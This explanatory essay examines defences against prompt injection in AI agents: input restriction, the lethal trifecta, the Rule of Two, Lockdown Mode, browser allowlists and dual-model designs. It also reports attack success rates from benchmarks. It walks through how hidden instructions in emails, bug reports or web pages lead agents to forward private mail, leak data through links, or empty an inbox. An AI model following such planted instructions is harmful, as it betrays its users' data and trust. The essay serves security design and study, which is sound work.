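# Restricting what an AI model is exposed to as a defence against adversarial inputs, and what the restriction costs

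## Why limit what a model reads?

An adversarial input is one designed to make an AI model behave in a way its operator or user does not want. One defence is to keep text an attacker could have written away from the part of the system that decides on sensitive actions. This works even if the model cannot recognise an attack, but it also prevents some legitimate tasks. If incoming emails cannot influence an assistant's actions, the assistant is safe from hostile emails, but it also cannot carry out the request "do what my landlord asks in the last email". Most work on this trade-off concerns language models that can act on a user's behalf and is only a few years old, although operating systems have kept untrusted programs away from sensitive functions for decades.

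### How an agent works

A language model takes in text and produces text, so it needs ordinary software to send an email or delete a file. An *agent* is a language model that uses such software in a loop. The model writes a request to use a tool, such as a mailbox, a web browser or a command line, and the software runs the tool and returns the result to the model. This repeats until the task is complete.

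*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) divides the loop into six steps. The agent receives a system prompt from its developer and a request from its user. It may fetch background documents from a database, and it may reason in writing about what to do next. The model then generates a tool call, which names a tool and gives its parameters, and the software executes the call. The tool's output is added to the *context*, the working text the model has accumulated so far, and the loop repeats from the step where documents are fetched.

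A language model receives the developer's rules, the user's request and the contents of any web page it reads as one text. Older software had a related problem with SQL injection, the attack that gave prompt injection its name. Someone types database commands into a form field, and a careless program passes them on as if they were its own. Programmers fixed this by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database never interprets the data as a command. A language model has no separate channel for data. Developers put markers between the parts of the context, but the markers are also text, and Wang and colleagues stress that the model still processes everything as a single sequence. A sentence on a web page that imitates an instruction from the user can therefore affect the output as a real one would. Wang and colleagues describe the result as a competition for attention,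 the mechanism by which a model weighs each piece of its context when it produces the next word, in which hostile text can draw weight away from the system prompt.

### One email, step by step

*Prompt injection* is an adversarial input made of instructions placed in text that a language model processes. Anthropic, which develops the Claude models, gives a simple example in its September 2026 system card (a developer's published safety report) for Claude Fable 5.1. Filled out a little, it goes like this:

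1. An attacker writes an ordinary-looking email and adds a line of hidden text, say in white letters on a white background, with an instruction to forward the last month of internal messages to a certain address. The mail server delivers it like any other email.
2. The user asks the agent to summarise the inbox. The request is harmless, and the user has no idea that the hidden line exists.
3. The model produces a call to the mailbox tool. The software runs the call and adds the text of the new emails to the context. The white letters become plain text like the rest.
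4. The model computes its next output from the whole context, which now includes the attacker's line. If the attack works, that output is a call to forward the messages.
5. The software finds that the call is well formed and that the agent has permission to send mail. It sends the messages.
6. A confirmation joins the context, and the model goes on to write the summary that the user wanted.

The attack worked without any component failing. The agent already had permission to read and send mail, and the attacker supplied only the sentence that led it to send mail in response to what it read. The attacker also didn't have to choose a victim, because the same email can go to a thousand inboxes and affect every susceptible agent that summarises one of them.

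Adversarial inputs are also a problem outside the laboratory. Through the EchoLeak vulnerability of 2025, a crafted email with hidden text could make Microsoft 365 Copilot, an office assistant, leak confidential data while it worked in the background, without the user clicking on or approving anything (Cross, 2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*).

### Which inputs, which actions

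*Untrusted input* is any data that an attacker could have written or altered, whatever it says. A harmless newsletter is therefore untrusted input, as are search results, comments on a code repository and the names of files that somebody else supplied. Wang and colleagues count the system prompt and the user's request as trusted, and tool results as untrusted, because the operator does not fully control the environment those results come from. They put background databases and training data in between. Most researchers trust both, but a few have shown attacks through them.

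The user's request is not always trustworthy. When a customer tries to talk a car dealer's chatbot into an enormous discount, the customer's message is the untrusted input and the dealer needs protection. Researchers call this *direct* injection, and they call it *indirect* injection when the hostile instructions are in third-party content, as in the email above. The distinction determines which route into the model a defence based on restricting inputs has to close, though Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) choose not to draw it in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. Some cases are mixed, as when an honest user pastes text from an attacker's website into the request. Research has been shifting towards indirect injection. Of the 37 papers on attacks that Wang and colleagues collected up to October 2025, 20 concern indirect injection, and 27 use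 instructions that a person would not notice.

A *consequential action* is a tool call that can do harm, such as sending data out, spending money, or changing or deleting files. An agent can also leak data without calling anything that looks like a "send" tool. If its answer contains an image link whose address includes a piece of the user's private data, the chat window sends that data to whoever runs the server when it loads the image. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore extend their requirements to the agent's text output, which must not carry data away through embedded links or manipulate what agents do later. Cross reports that OpenAI's testers, working in simulated environments, found injections that made an agent copy the hostile text into its own emails, files and chat posts, where the next agent would read it.

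### Resisting an attack, or making it harmless

Developers can respond by making the model resist injection. They can also assume that an attack will sometimes succeed and arrange the system so that success achieves little. (Nothing stops them from doing both.)

Ways to resist attacks include training the model on examples of them, warning against them in the system prompt, and running detectors, which are separate programs, often models themselves, that scan incoming text or outgoing tool calls for signs of an attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues regard all of these as heuristics. A detector makes attacks harder because the attacker must deceive the detector as well as the main model, but both are fallible, so protection is not guaranteed. The researchers also have reservations about asking the user to confirm each sensitive action, because it slows the work down and tired or overloaded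 people approve things they should not.

Under their alternative, once an agent has read untrusted input, its designers must constrain it so that the input cannot trigger a consequential action, regardless of how suspicious the text looks. In the email example, the software would refuse to forward, delete or send anything at the model's request once the inbox text entered the context. The hidden line could still spoil the summary by making the model omit an important message or invent one. It could not send the internal messages to an outsider, provided that the designers had also prevented leaks through links. Designs that apply the principle range from a fixed menu of permitted actions to pairs of models in which only one may read outside text.

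Simon Willison, a programmer who has written about prompt injection for years, argues in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) that anyone who can get text into a model's context should be treated as having complete control over what the model produces next, including tool calls. This is too pessimistic as a description of current models, because most injections fail, but it is useful as a design rule because designers don't need to know how many fail. The drawback is that the rule treats a harmless newsletter the same way as an attack.

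One reason to limit what a model reads is that models may not soon resist adversarial inputs reliably. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees as long as both the agents and their defences rely on the current class of language models. Part of their reason is the history of image recognition. Changes to an image's pixels that are too small for a person to notice can make a classifier name the wrong object. Researchers described these adversarial images more than a decade ago and still haven't solved the problem, despite working on it ever since. It is in some ways easier than protecting a language model, because a classifier only chooses a label, while a language model can produce any text.

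The record of defences for language models was already poor, and it got worse in October 2025, when *The Attacker Moves Second*, by Nasr and colleagues, reported that attacks adapted to each defence had defeated a dozen published defences. A review by Wang and colleagues points to a likely reason those defences had seemed effective. Researchers who propose defences still mostly test them against hand-written templates, whereas 14 of the 37 attack papers in the review use automated search to find effective attacks. According to The Decoder, OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

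This argument generalises from a poor record of resistance, so it does not prove that resistance must fail. That record has since improved a good deal.

### How well the newest models resist

In late 2025, a single strong attack succeeded in 4.7% of cases against Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 on a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. The success rate rose to 33.6% with ten attempts and 63% with a hundred, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, and rival models did worse. Claude was particularly vulnerable when controlling a computer through its screen. VentureBeat reported that a single attempt against Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, succeeded 17.8% of the time in that setting, and that the rate reached 78.6% by the 200th attempt.

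By autumn 2026 attack success rates were far lower. Gray Swan had built a newer benchmark from a large public competition in which people wrote injections against leading models (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026). OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta and the British and American government AI institutes took part in the study. The version in the September system card has 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks, which Gray Swan chose because they worked across several models. Anthropic reports that attacks on Claude Fable 5.1 succeeded 0.1% of the time with one attempt, 0.7% with ten and 1.0% with fifteen. After fifteen attempts, the rate was 9.2% for the best model from another company and between 24% and 53% for most of the others.

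OpenAI's models have been less robust to indirect prompt injection than to direct injection, and the indirect results are the relevant ones for an agent that constantly reads other people's text. Cross reports that in the tests for OpenAI's *GPT-6 Sol and GPT-6 Luna* (2026), GPT-6 Sol scored 99.99% for robustness against direct injection but 97.13% against indirect injection. For its predecessor, TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gave failure rates in August of about 0.05% for direct attacks and 3.77% for indirect ones.

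Each of these percentages depends on the attacks used as well as the model, so they are less solid than their decimal places suggest. When Anthropic released Claude Opus 5, attackers succeeded in 2.0% of cases after fifteen attempts on Gray Swan's benchmark, according to The Decoder. The September card gives 4.8% for the same model, but Anthropic had added nine scenarios and 670 attacks to the report, which probably explains most of the rise. On PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of long office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio, the rate for Opus 5 is 10.0% with five attempts per case, level with the newer Claude Fable 5.2. The rate is 7.6% for GPT-6 Astra and 2.4% for Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, while the average over the 21 models in the original set was 34.9%. PromptArmor sells AI security and has a commercial reason to find weaknesses, just as a developer has a reason to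 report few. Even so, the two benchmarks' results for Opus 5 differ too widely for either to be quoted as the model's overall rate.

Determined attackers succeed much more often than any of these averages suggest. Anthropic's own tests use Shade, an automated attacker that Gray Swan trains on the test scenarios. Shade gets 200 attempts at each coding scenario. The table counts scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded. The added safeguards are detectors that inspect tool results before the model acts on them and, in the browser test, also a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls.

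| Test | Model | Attempts per scenario | Broken without added safeguards | Broken with them |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web browser, attacks developed on an older model | Fable 5.1 | 10 | 10 of 110 | 0 of 110 |
| Screen control, Shade | Fable 5.1 | 200 | 2 of 14 | 2 of 14 |
| Coding, earlier Shade | Fable 5.1 | 200 | 31 of 40 | 18 of 40 |
| Coding, stronger Shade | Fable 5.1 | 200 | 38 of 40 | 36 of 40 |
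| Coding, stronger Shade | Opus 5 | 200 | 40 of 40 | 40 of 40 |

The coding figures for Fable 5.1 include responses from an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, because a separate filter against cybersecurity misuse hands some requests over to it. Every success of the stronger attacker came through Opus 4.8, and none of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. This is an impressive result for Fable 5.1, but it offers users limited reassurance because the product makes the same handovers. With Opus 5, some of the attacks succeeded against the model itself.

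### What a small rate means

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*. If *p* is 2.87%, which is 100% minus GPT-6 Sol's score, an attacker's chance of at least one success passes 50% at the 24th attempt. If *p* is 0.1%, reaching 50% takes about 700 attempts, and 1,000 attempts give a 63% chance.

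Real attempts are not independent, so the formula exaggerates what blind repetition can do. Starting from the old figure of 4.7% for Opus 4.5, it predicts 38% after ten attempts and 99% after a hundred, but Gray Swan measured 33.6% and 63%. Some tasks evidently withstand a whole series of attacks while others fail early. The formula also leaves out learning, which helps the attacker. In one OpenAI test, the company's automated attacker, GPT-Red, broke GPT-5.1 in 84% of the scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. Once an attacker has a text that works, they can also send out thousands of copies at almost no extra expense.

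Anthropic objects that tests like the one with Shade deliberately favour the attacker, because an outsider does not know exactly how a company has set up its agent, and repeated attempts make detection more likely. This is a fair point about a patient attack on one well-monitored company. It is weaker when the attacker sends one email to each of many inboxes, because no victim sees repeated attempts and the attacker can rehearse beforehand on a private copy of a popular product.

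A perfect test score does not rule out successful attacks either. With no successes in 110 browser scenarios, the 95% confidence limit still allows a true success rate of up to about 2.7%, and that limit assumes that future attacks resemble the ones in the test. Willison made much the same point in June 2026 about a system that had withstood some 6,000 attempts. By the same arithmetic, 6,000 failed attempts put the rate below about 0.05% for attacks of the kinds already tried, but set no limit for cleverer ones. Willison (2026) granted that the laboratories' training had made injection much harder, but still advised against deploying any system in which a successful injection could do irreversible damage.

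## What is lost when a whole input channel is closed?

Developers can keep a successful injection from doing irreversible damage by removing something the attack depends on. They can close an *input channel*, a route by which data reaches the model, such as web pages, incoming mail or stored memory. Or they can leave the channel open and remove one of the model's abilities, such as reading private files or sending messages. Both measures are crude because they take a feature away from every user, including the great majority whom nobody would have attacked. But they are fairly easy to build and check, and several companies now offer them in ordinary products.

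### The lethal trifecta

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) identifies three features of an agent that together let an attacker steal data through prompt injection: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a means of communicating with the outside world that could carry the data off. The agent reads the attacker's instruction, fetches the data and sends it out. If any one of the three features is missing, this kind of theft fails.

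The ability to communicate is the easiest of these features to overlook. Willison points out that, besides the image links already mentioned, any tool that makes a web request can send data out, whether it calls an online service or offers the user a link to click. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that sites commonly log the addresses visitors request. An injection can therefore steal a user's account number by making the agent open a page on the attacker's site with that number at the end of the address. This means an agent with live web access can send data out even if it has no tool for sending anything.

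In a 2025 case, one tool had all three features. GitHub, where programmers store and share code, provides an official server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting agents to outside tools. The server let an agent read its user's private code as well as bug reports on public projects, which anyone can file. The agent could also open pull requests, which are proposed changes to a project. An attacker could file a bug report containing instructions, and an agent that obeyed them would copy material from the private code into a pull request that the attacker could read.

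Removing any one of the features would have stopped this theft, at a different price each time:

- Without the public bug reports, strangers have no way to instruct the agent through them. It can still damage the code by mistake, and it can no longer help with bug reports, which is much of what the owner of a public project wants from it.
- Without access to private code, an injection finds nothing secret to copy, though it can still make the agent propose a bad change to the public project. Somebody who works on a single public project loses almost nothing.
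- Without the power to publish, the agent prepares its change and a person submits it. The secret stays in as long as that person notices it among the changed lines. Projects that review every change anyway pay little extra for this.

Willison lists 17 reported cases of this kind of attack from April 2023 to June 2025, in products including ChatGPT, Slack and Google's Bard. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out. No vendor can do that when a user combines tools from different makers. One company's mail tool and another's web tool may each be reasonable alone but complete the trifecta when the same agent has both. Willison advises people who mix tools this way to avoid the trifecta altogether.

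### The Rule of Two

The trifecta describes theft, but an injection can do a lot of harm without stealing anything. eWeek's *Claude-for-Chrome Pilot* reports that in one of Anthropic's 2025 tests of its browser agent, a fake email told Claude to delete all the user's messages "for security reasons", and Claude emptied the inbox without asking. No data left the mailbox, so blocking communication with the outside would not have helped.

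Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers such cases by widening the last of the three properties. Until research makes it possible to detect and refuse injections reliably, Meta proposes, an agent should have at most two of these within a session:

- [A] it can process untrustworthy inputs
- [B] it can access sensitive systems or private data
- [C] it can change state or communicate externally

Changing state means altering something that lasts, such as a file, a booking or an account setting. A session ends when the agent restarts with an empty context, which removes any text from the attacker. If a task needs all three properties in one session, Meta says the agent should not act autonomously. At a minimum, a person must approve its actions or another reliable check must validate them.

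The name comes from a 2019 guideline for Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome. Under the guideline, as Willison (2025) quotes it in *Chromium Docs*, programmers should combine no more than two of three things: untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

Meta describes three hypothetical agents, each lacking a different property. A travel assistant searches the web and holds the user's personal details [AB], so a person must confirm every reservation and payment, and the agent may open only addresses returned by trusted sources, not ones it composed. A research assistant visits any site and fills in forms [AC], but it runs in an isolated browser with no saved logins and gets little private information beyond the user's request. A coding agent changes a company's live systems [BC] with few human checks, so software filters everything the agent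 reads according to who wrote it. People can restore material that the filter wrongly blocks.

In these examples, "removing" a property often means limiting it. The travel assistant can still spend money once the user agrees, and Meta concedes that a compliant design can fail when a user blindly confirms a warning.

Critics found a larger problem in the rule's diagram, which originally labelled each pair of properties "safe". Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, liked the rule but objected that an agent with [A] and [C] can do harm even without access to private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that [B] covers every sensitive system, whether or not it holds private data. An agent without [B] may write and communicate freely, but only where nothing important can happen, such as in a sealed test environment. Meta also changed the diagram's label from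 "safe" to "lower risk".

Ayzenberg's reply makes the rule consistent, but applying it now depends largely on what counts as sensitive. Suppose an agent reads the web and posts comments on public forums from a throwaway account. It has no access to secrets or company systems, yet an injection could make it post libel or thousands of fraudulent links. If the forum counts as a sensitive system, the agent has all three properties; otherwise it obeys the rule and can still do this harm. The other pairs also leave risks. An agent with [A] and [B] can mislead its user, which Meta counts among the lower-consequence effects of injection and leaves outside the rule. An agent with [B] and [C] faces no hostile text but can still wreck a live system by mistake.

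### Auditing one assistant

Suppose an assistant reads its user's mail, searches the web and sends messages. The user tells it, "Anna's email says our hotel has cancelled. Find another one nearby and let her know." Applying either rule requires noting what each of the assistant's features contributes.

| Feature | Untrusted content | Private data | Way out, or lasting change |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading mail | Yes, anyone can write to the address | Yes, possibly years of it | Yes, if the tool can also delete or move mail |
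| Searching and opening web pages | Yes | Only if the browser is logged in | Yes, through the addresses it requests |
| Sending messages | No | Perhaps the address book | Yes |
| Displaying answers | No | No | Yes, if the window loads images from the web |

The table shows that switching off only web search or only the sending tool does not prevent theft, because a property remains as long as any feature supplies it. With web search off, strangers can still write to the mailbox and the model can still send messages, which is enough for a theft. With the sending tool off, the model still has the mailbox and the web, and data can leave through web addresses.

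To take away untrusted content, the developer stops web search and lets through only mail from people the user has chosen. Meta suggests close friends. Ordinary software has to do the filtering before the model sees anything, including subject lines and senders' names, and it has to verify where a message came from, because senders can forge addresses. A stranger's instructions then never arrive. The instructions of someone who has broken into Anna's account do, and so does a hostile newsletter that Anna innocently forwards. The price is high. The assistant can read Anna's email and answer it but cannot look for a hotel, and in daily use it misses every invoice, delivery notice and first message from somebody new. (Other designs let an agent handle such mail while the model that chooses its actions never reads it.)

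Removing private data means giving the assistant no access to the mailbox and having it send from its own account. The account has to be separate because the ability to write in the user's name is sensitive even if the assistant cannot read old messages. An injection on a hotel's website could then only steal what the user typed into the request or make the assistant send junk from its own address. The hotel task still works if the user types in Anna's address, the town and the dates. But the user now has to read all the mail, which makes the product much less useful as a mail assistant.

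The remaining option is to limit what the assistant can send out or change. The assistant writes a draft and the user sends it. Web search uses stored copies of pages, the mail tool cannot delete or move anything, and the chat window loads no outside images. Hostile text can still make the assistant recommend a fraudulent hotel or put a bad link into the draft. In the hotel task, the user has to click once to send the message, the stored pages don't show which rooms are free tonight, and the assistant cannot book the room.

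OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) considers an agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies. Having a user approve each message limits what the agent sends, but the agent has still read sensitive records and could disclose them by another permitted path. OpenAI therefore recommends limiting the data an agent can access as well as its outgoing actions. The mail assistant, for example, could be allowed to open only the last week's messages rather than the whole archive.

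Meta also allows a milder version in which the assistant may write to trusted recipients without asking. Anna gets her answer at once, and the assistant cannot send a stolen file straight to a stranger. But the attacker's words can still reach Anna, and her own assistant may read them.

The pair of properties can also change partway through a task. In Meta's example, an agent starts on the open internet without access to internal systems, then loses its ability to communicate when it gains that access. The switch has to be one-way, because once the context contains both web text and private data, restoring communication would complete the chain. Using the web first and private data second suits many tasks, but the hotel request needs the opposite order, because the mail assistant has to learn the town from Anna's email before it can look up hotels.

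This assistant loses the least usefulness if it is stopped from sending data out, and Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, takes the same view of AI systems in general. The GitHub agent is different, because someone who uses it on one public project loses almost nothing by removing its access to private data. An agent whose whole job is to book, buy or repair things is of little use if it can't make lasting changes.

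### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI offers a restriction of this kind in ChatGPT as an optional setting called Lockdown Mode. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (OpenAI, 2026) announced it for organisations in February, and a June update extended it to personal accounts. OpenAI first said the setting was meant for a small group with high security needs, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and that most people do not need it. The June update also recommends it when a user is willing to give up some functions for stricter protection.

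The setting mainly controls outgoing data. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, it limits network requests to try to block the last stage of data theft, but it does not keep prompt injections out of what ChatGPT reads. The table lists its effects on incoming and outgoing data separately.

| Restriction | Effect on what comes in | Effect on what goes out |
|---|---|---|
| Web browsing uses only cached (stored) pages | Hostile pages may be among them; results may be old or missing | No live request reaches an outside site |
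| ChatGPT retrieves no images from the web | Users can still upload images | Image addresses cannot carry data away |
| Deep research (long automated web research) and agent mode are off | ChatGPT reads fewer outside pages | The requests and actions of both features stop |
| Code written in Canvas, a workspace inside ChatGPT, has no network access | The code cannot fetch outside data | The code cannot send data |
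| ChatGPT downloads no files for analysis | Users must upload files themselves, and those may be hostile | No download request leaves |

The setting does not change memory, file uploads or the sharing of conversations, so a hostile instruction in an uploaded document or a cached page can still make an answer wrong. OpenAI does not promise that theft is impossible, and it lists connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques as remaining risks. The setting also does not change network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

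On personal accounts, ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode blocks connected apps from accessing outside services live and from making changes that conflict with the protection. The finance and shopping features also become unavailable. In company-managed workspaces, important work may depend on apps, so OpenAI lets administrators decide which ones stay on. It advises them to enable only apps they trust, and to let even those apps write only when they can confirm that an attacker would not see the result. For example, an attacker could see a comment on a public bug tracker, but probably not a note in a private calendar.

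According to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, ChatGPT loses most of what makes its agent and research features useful when it is in Lockdown Mode. Users can reduce this loss by switching the mode off for a single chat, but they then have to recognise which chats are risky.

In return, users get a control that does not depend on a model's judgement. Willison welcomed it for that reason, but noted that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined data thief. The default settings do include a narrower check on outgoing data. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a mechanism that tries to detect when a request would pass information from the conversation to a third party. It then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the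 agent to find another way. Most browsing continues as normal, so this check disrupts users far less than Lockdown Mode, but it protects only against the leaks it detects.

A fixed restriction can also have flaws. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported in November 2026 that researchers had bypassed Lockdown Mode and reached a user's chat history, and that OpenAI had patched the flaw.

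### Browsers that limit which sites an agent reads

An agent inside a web browser can easily have all three properties, because it reads pages written by strangers, works in the user's logged-in accounts and can click on anything. Several makers limit which sites their agents may visit.

Microsoft previewed an agent for its Edge browser in October 2025. Microsoft's *Considerations for Safe Agentic Browsing* (2025) says that by default the agent needed the user's approval to open any site not on a curated list. In a stricter mode, the user had to approve every site. Microsoft also removed powers that an injection might exploit, so the agent could not use saved passwords or other form data, download files, open other programs or change the browser's settings.

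Edge for Business keeps the allowlist. According to Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot*, the agent works only on domains that administrators have authorised, and is unavailable if the list is empty. For consumers, Microsoft describes blocklists of high-risk sites, such as gambling sites, and lets users add their own. This restricts users much less, but a blocklist admits every hostile page that nobody has reported yet. The consumer agent still has no access to saved passwords, but it shares the browser's cookies, the small files that keep a user signed in, so it is logged in wherever the user is. Microsoft suggests a fresh browser profile for people who want to avoid that.

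*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a design in which the list of allowed sites depends on the task. A separate component, which is never exposed to web content, decides which sites are relevant to the user's request. It keeps one list of sites the agent may read and another of sites where the agent may also click and type. If a page contains a frame from an unrelated site, such as an advertisement, the browser does not pass the frame to the model. Chrome also checks any address the model composes and allows only known, public ones, which makes it harder to hide private data in an address.

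The first version Google shipped tracked only the list of sites where the agent may both read and act, and Parker says the team would tune the system to reduce unnecessary friction. In August 2026, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) still described limiting the agent to sites strictly relevant to the task as one of Chrome's main protections. A list that changes with the task is less of a burden than a fixed one, since a recipe site can be open for one task and closed for the next. But the protection then depends partly on a judgement of which sites are relevant, and that judgement can be wrong.

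A browser agent can also have access to the whole web but not to the user's accounts. OpenAI's Atlas browser has a "logged out mode" that works this way. Willison called it very smart and was much more worried about the logged-in mode, where users have to make security decisions that few are equipped to make. Without a login, the agent can still compare products and do research nearly as well, but it can't read the user's mail or change a booking.

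Anthropic combines these measures in its own browser extension and leaves many of the choices to the customer. Its *Claude in Chrome admin controls* recommends that companies start with a restrictive allowlist and extend it as they gain experience. *Use Claude in Chrome safely* similarly advises individual users to begin with trusted sites and to use a separate browser profile with no access to sensitive accounts such as banking. The extension is initially off for organisations that have switched on Anthropic's settings for American health-privacy law. Even after they enable it, it blocks every site until an administrator allows one or changes this default.

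Every site list has a weakness, because a trustworthy site can carry text by untrustworthy people. Parker names user reviews as one place where injections can appear, and hiding unrelated frames removes advertisements but not reviews. Anthropic tells users to avoid sites with content from unknown people, but these include most social networks, many shops and every webmail service. If an administrator puts the company's webmail on the allowlist, anyone who knows an employee's address can write to the agent. An allowlist containing only GitHub would still have let through the hostile bug report in the 2025 case.

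## How can a system use data its planning model never reads?

A site allowlist or a mail filter keeps strangers' text out of the whole system, so the assistant cannot use it. Other designs let the text in but keep it from influencing the *planning model*, which chooses what tools to call and in what order. The system can then forward or summarise an email without the email's contents affecting what the system does next.

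These designs differ in how they handle a request described by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, in which a user asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The calendar is untrusted because anyone can send the user an invitation. One of today's entries might contain an instruction to forward the user's recent mail to an outside address, and an ordinary agent would read that entry before choosing its next tool call.

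### Choosing from a fixed menu

The strictest design is the *action selector*. The model reads the user's request, picks one of a fixed set of actions and never receives the result. A customer service chatbot might send a customer a link to their last order, or direct them to the settings page to change a password. An action can also have blanks for the model to fill in. For example, the model might put a product name from the request into a prepared database query.

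The schedule request works only if a developer has already written an action for it:

```
email_schedule(day="today", to="boss")
```

Ordinary code behind this action reads the calendar, copies the entries into an email, looks up the boss's address and sends the message. The model has finished its work before the code opens the calendar, so the hostile entry can't affect the choice of action. The entry still reaches the boss's inbox word for word.

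The user's own text can still affect which action the model picks, so the menu should contain only actions that any user may take. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a furniture shop's chatbot that runs a request only if it closely resembles one on an approved list. A malicious customer might get past the comparison, but would still only trigger something the shop had approved. However, the chatbot refuses reasonable requests that nobody foresaw, and developers have to do most of the work in advance. An assistant meant to find "all tax-related PDF files" gains little from a language model if developers have already fixed every search it can run.

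### Dropping the user's text

*Context minimization* defends against a hostile user. The model turns the user's request into a query, software deletes the request from the context, and the model then writes its reply from the query's results. If a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for an enormous discount, the request can affect which cars the database looks up, but it is no longer in the context when the model writes the quote.

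Deleting text from a model's context blocks an injection only if nothing derived from that text remains. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms, passes the summary to a database or a doctor, and explains the diagnosis. If the software deletes the patient's message but keeps the summary, an injection can remain in the summary. Deleting the summary as well prevents that, but the chatbot then can't use anything the patient said in its explanation.

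The user also keeps some influence over the query. Another of their examples is a chatbot that answers questions about a medicine by showing passages from its leaflet. A user cannot make it show a made-up passage, but might get it to leave out the one on contraindications.

Context minimization does not protect the schedule request, because the attacker's instruction is in the calendar. Deleting the user's request would leave that instruction in the model's context.

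### Fixing the plan first

With *plan-then-execute*, the model writes its list of tool calls from the user's request before any tool runs. It may read the results afterwards, but software runs only the calls on the list. For the schedule, the plan has two calls and a blank:

```
calendar.read(today)
email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The software fixes this list before it opens the calendar, so the hostile entry cannot change which actions run. The model later reads the entry to fill the blank, and the entry may well cause it to produce a call that forwards the user's mail. The software does not run that call because it is not in the plan. The plan also fixes the email's recipient, but the attacker can still put anything in the body.

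The protection depends on how much of each call the plan fixes. If a file assistant's plan fixes only which commands it will use, one to find files and another to move them, an injection can make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive without departing from the plan. Some tasks also need arguments that the plan can't fix in advance. If the user says, "Reply to this email with the information the sender is requesting", the assistant cannot know what to search for until it has read the email. A hostile sender could make it search for extra confidential information and hide the results in the reply as invisible characters.

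A fixed plan can still allow for data that is unknown when the plan is made. To tell the user's regular collaborators about a holiday, for example, a mail assistant has to email an unknown number of people it has yet to identify, so its plan needs a step that repeats for each of them. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think that the choice and order of a mail assistant's actions should rarely depend on untrusted data, and that most uses would therefore lose nothing from a fixed plan. An assistant that answers questions from a database loses more, because it can no longer look at a query's results, notice that they don't answer the question and try a different query.

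### Separating planning from reading

Under plan-then-execute, a single model both plans and reads the calendar. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed splitting these jobs between two models. The planning model takes the user's request and can call tools, while a *quarantined model* reads untrusted input and cannot call tools. The controller between them is an ordinary program that runs the tools and holds the data. It gives each piece of untrusted data a name, called a *variable*, which the planning model uses without seeing the data.

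The schedule request then goes like this:

1. The planning model asks for today's calendar. The controller fetches the entries and stores them as `$VAR1`.
2. The planning model asks the quarantined model to turn `$VAR1` into a tidy list. The controller puts the real entries into the quarantined model's prompt and stores its answer as `$VAR2`.
3. The planning model asks to email `$VAR2` to the boss. The controller inserts the text and sends the message.

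The hostile entry cannot instruct the planning model because, in the first step, the controller stores it under a name instead of adding it to that model's context. The entry still reaches the quarantined model, which Willison assumes may be compromised at any moment. If that happens, the quarantined model can produce bad text but cannot forward anyone's mail.

The split has two advantages over a plan fixed in advance. The planning model can choose each call after the previous one has finished, because it has read nothing from the attacker. And the model that writes the email's text has access only to the calendar, so it can't fetch confidential mail to hide in the message. This second advantage is smaller when the task supplies private data. For example, a quarantined model that drafts a reply from the user's recent emails can leak them in the draft.

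Willison called his solution "pretty bad". The planning model treats everything the user enters as trusted, so an attack gets through if the user pastes in hostile text. The quarantined model's output also reaches the user's screen, where it might persuade the user to copy a block of scrambled private data into an attacker's website. Willison worried most about complexity, because one programming mistake that passes the quarantined model's text to the planning model undoes all the protection.

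### Variable passing, step by step

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) present an algorithm for variable passing in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* and implement it in FIDES, an agent system from Microsoft. The algorithm keeps a history, which the planning model reads, and a memory, which the model does not read.

1. Code adds the user's request to the history and passes the history to the planning model, along with a list of the available tools.
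2. The planning model produces a tool call. Each argument is either an actual value, such as an address from the request, or the name of a variable.
3. Code looks up each variable in the memory, substitutes its value and runs the tool. The history records the call with the name still in place.
4. When the tool returns a result, code creates a fresh name, stores the result under it in the memory and adds only the name to the history.
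5. Code passes the history to the planning model again. Steps 2 to 4 repeat until the model writes its final answer.

For the schedule, the calls and the names they return would look like this:

```
calendar.read(today)                              -> #calendar_0
query_llm("Make a tidy list", #calendar_0)        -> #query_llm_0
email.write(#query_llm_0, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The middle call goes to the quarantined model. If the boss doesn't mind raw calendar entries, the planning model can skip that call and put `#calendar_0` straight into the email. Then no model reads the entries.

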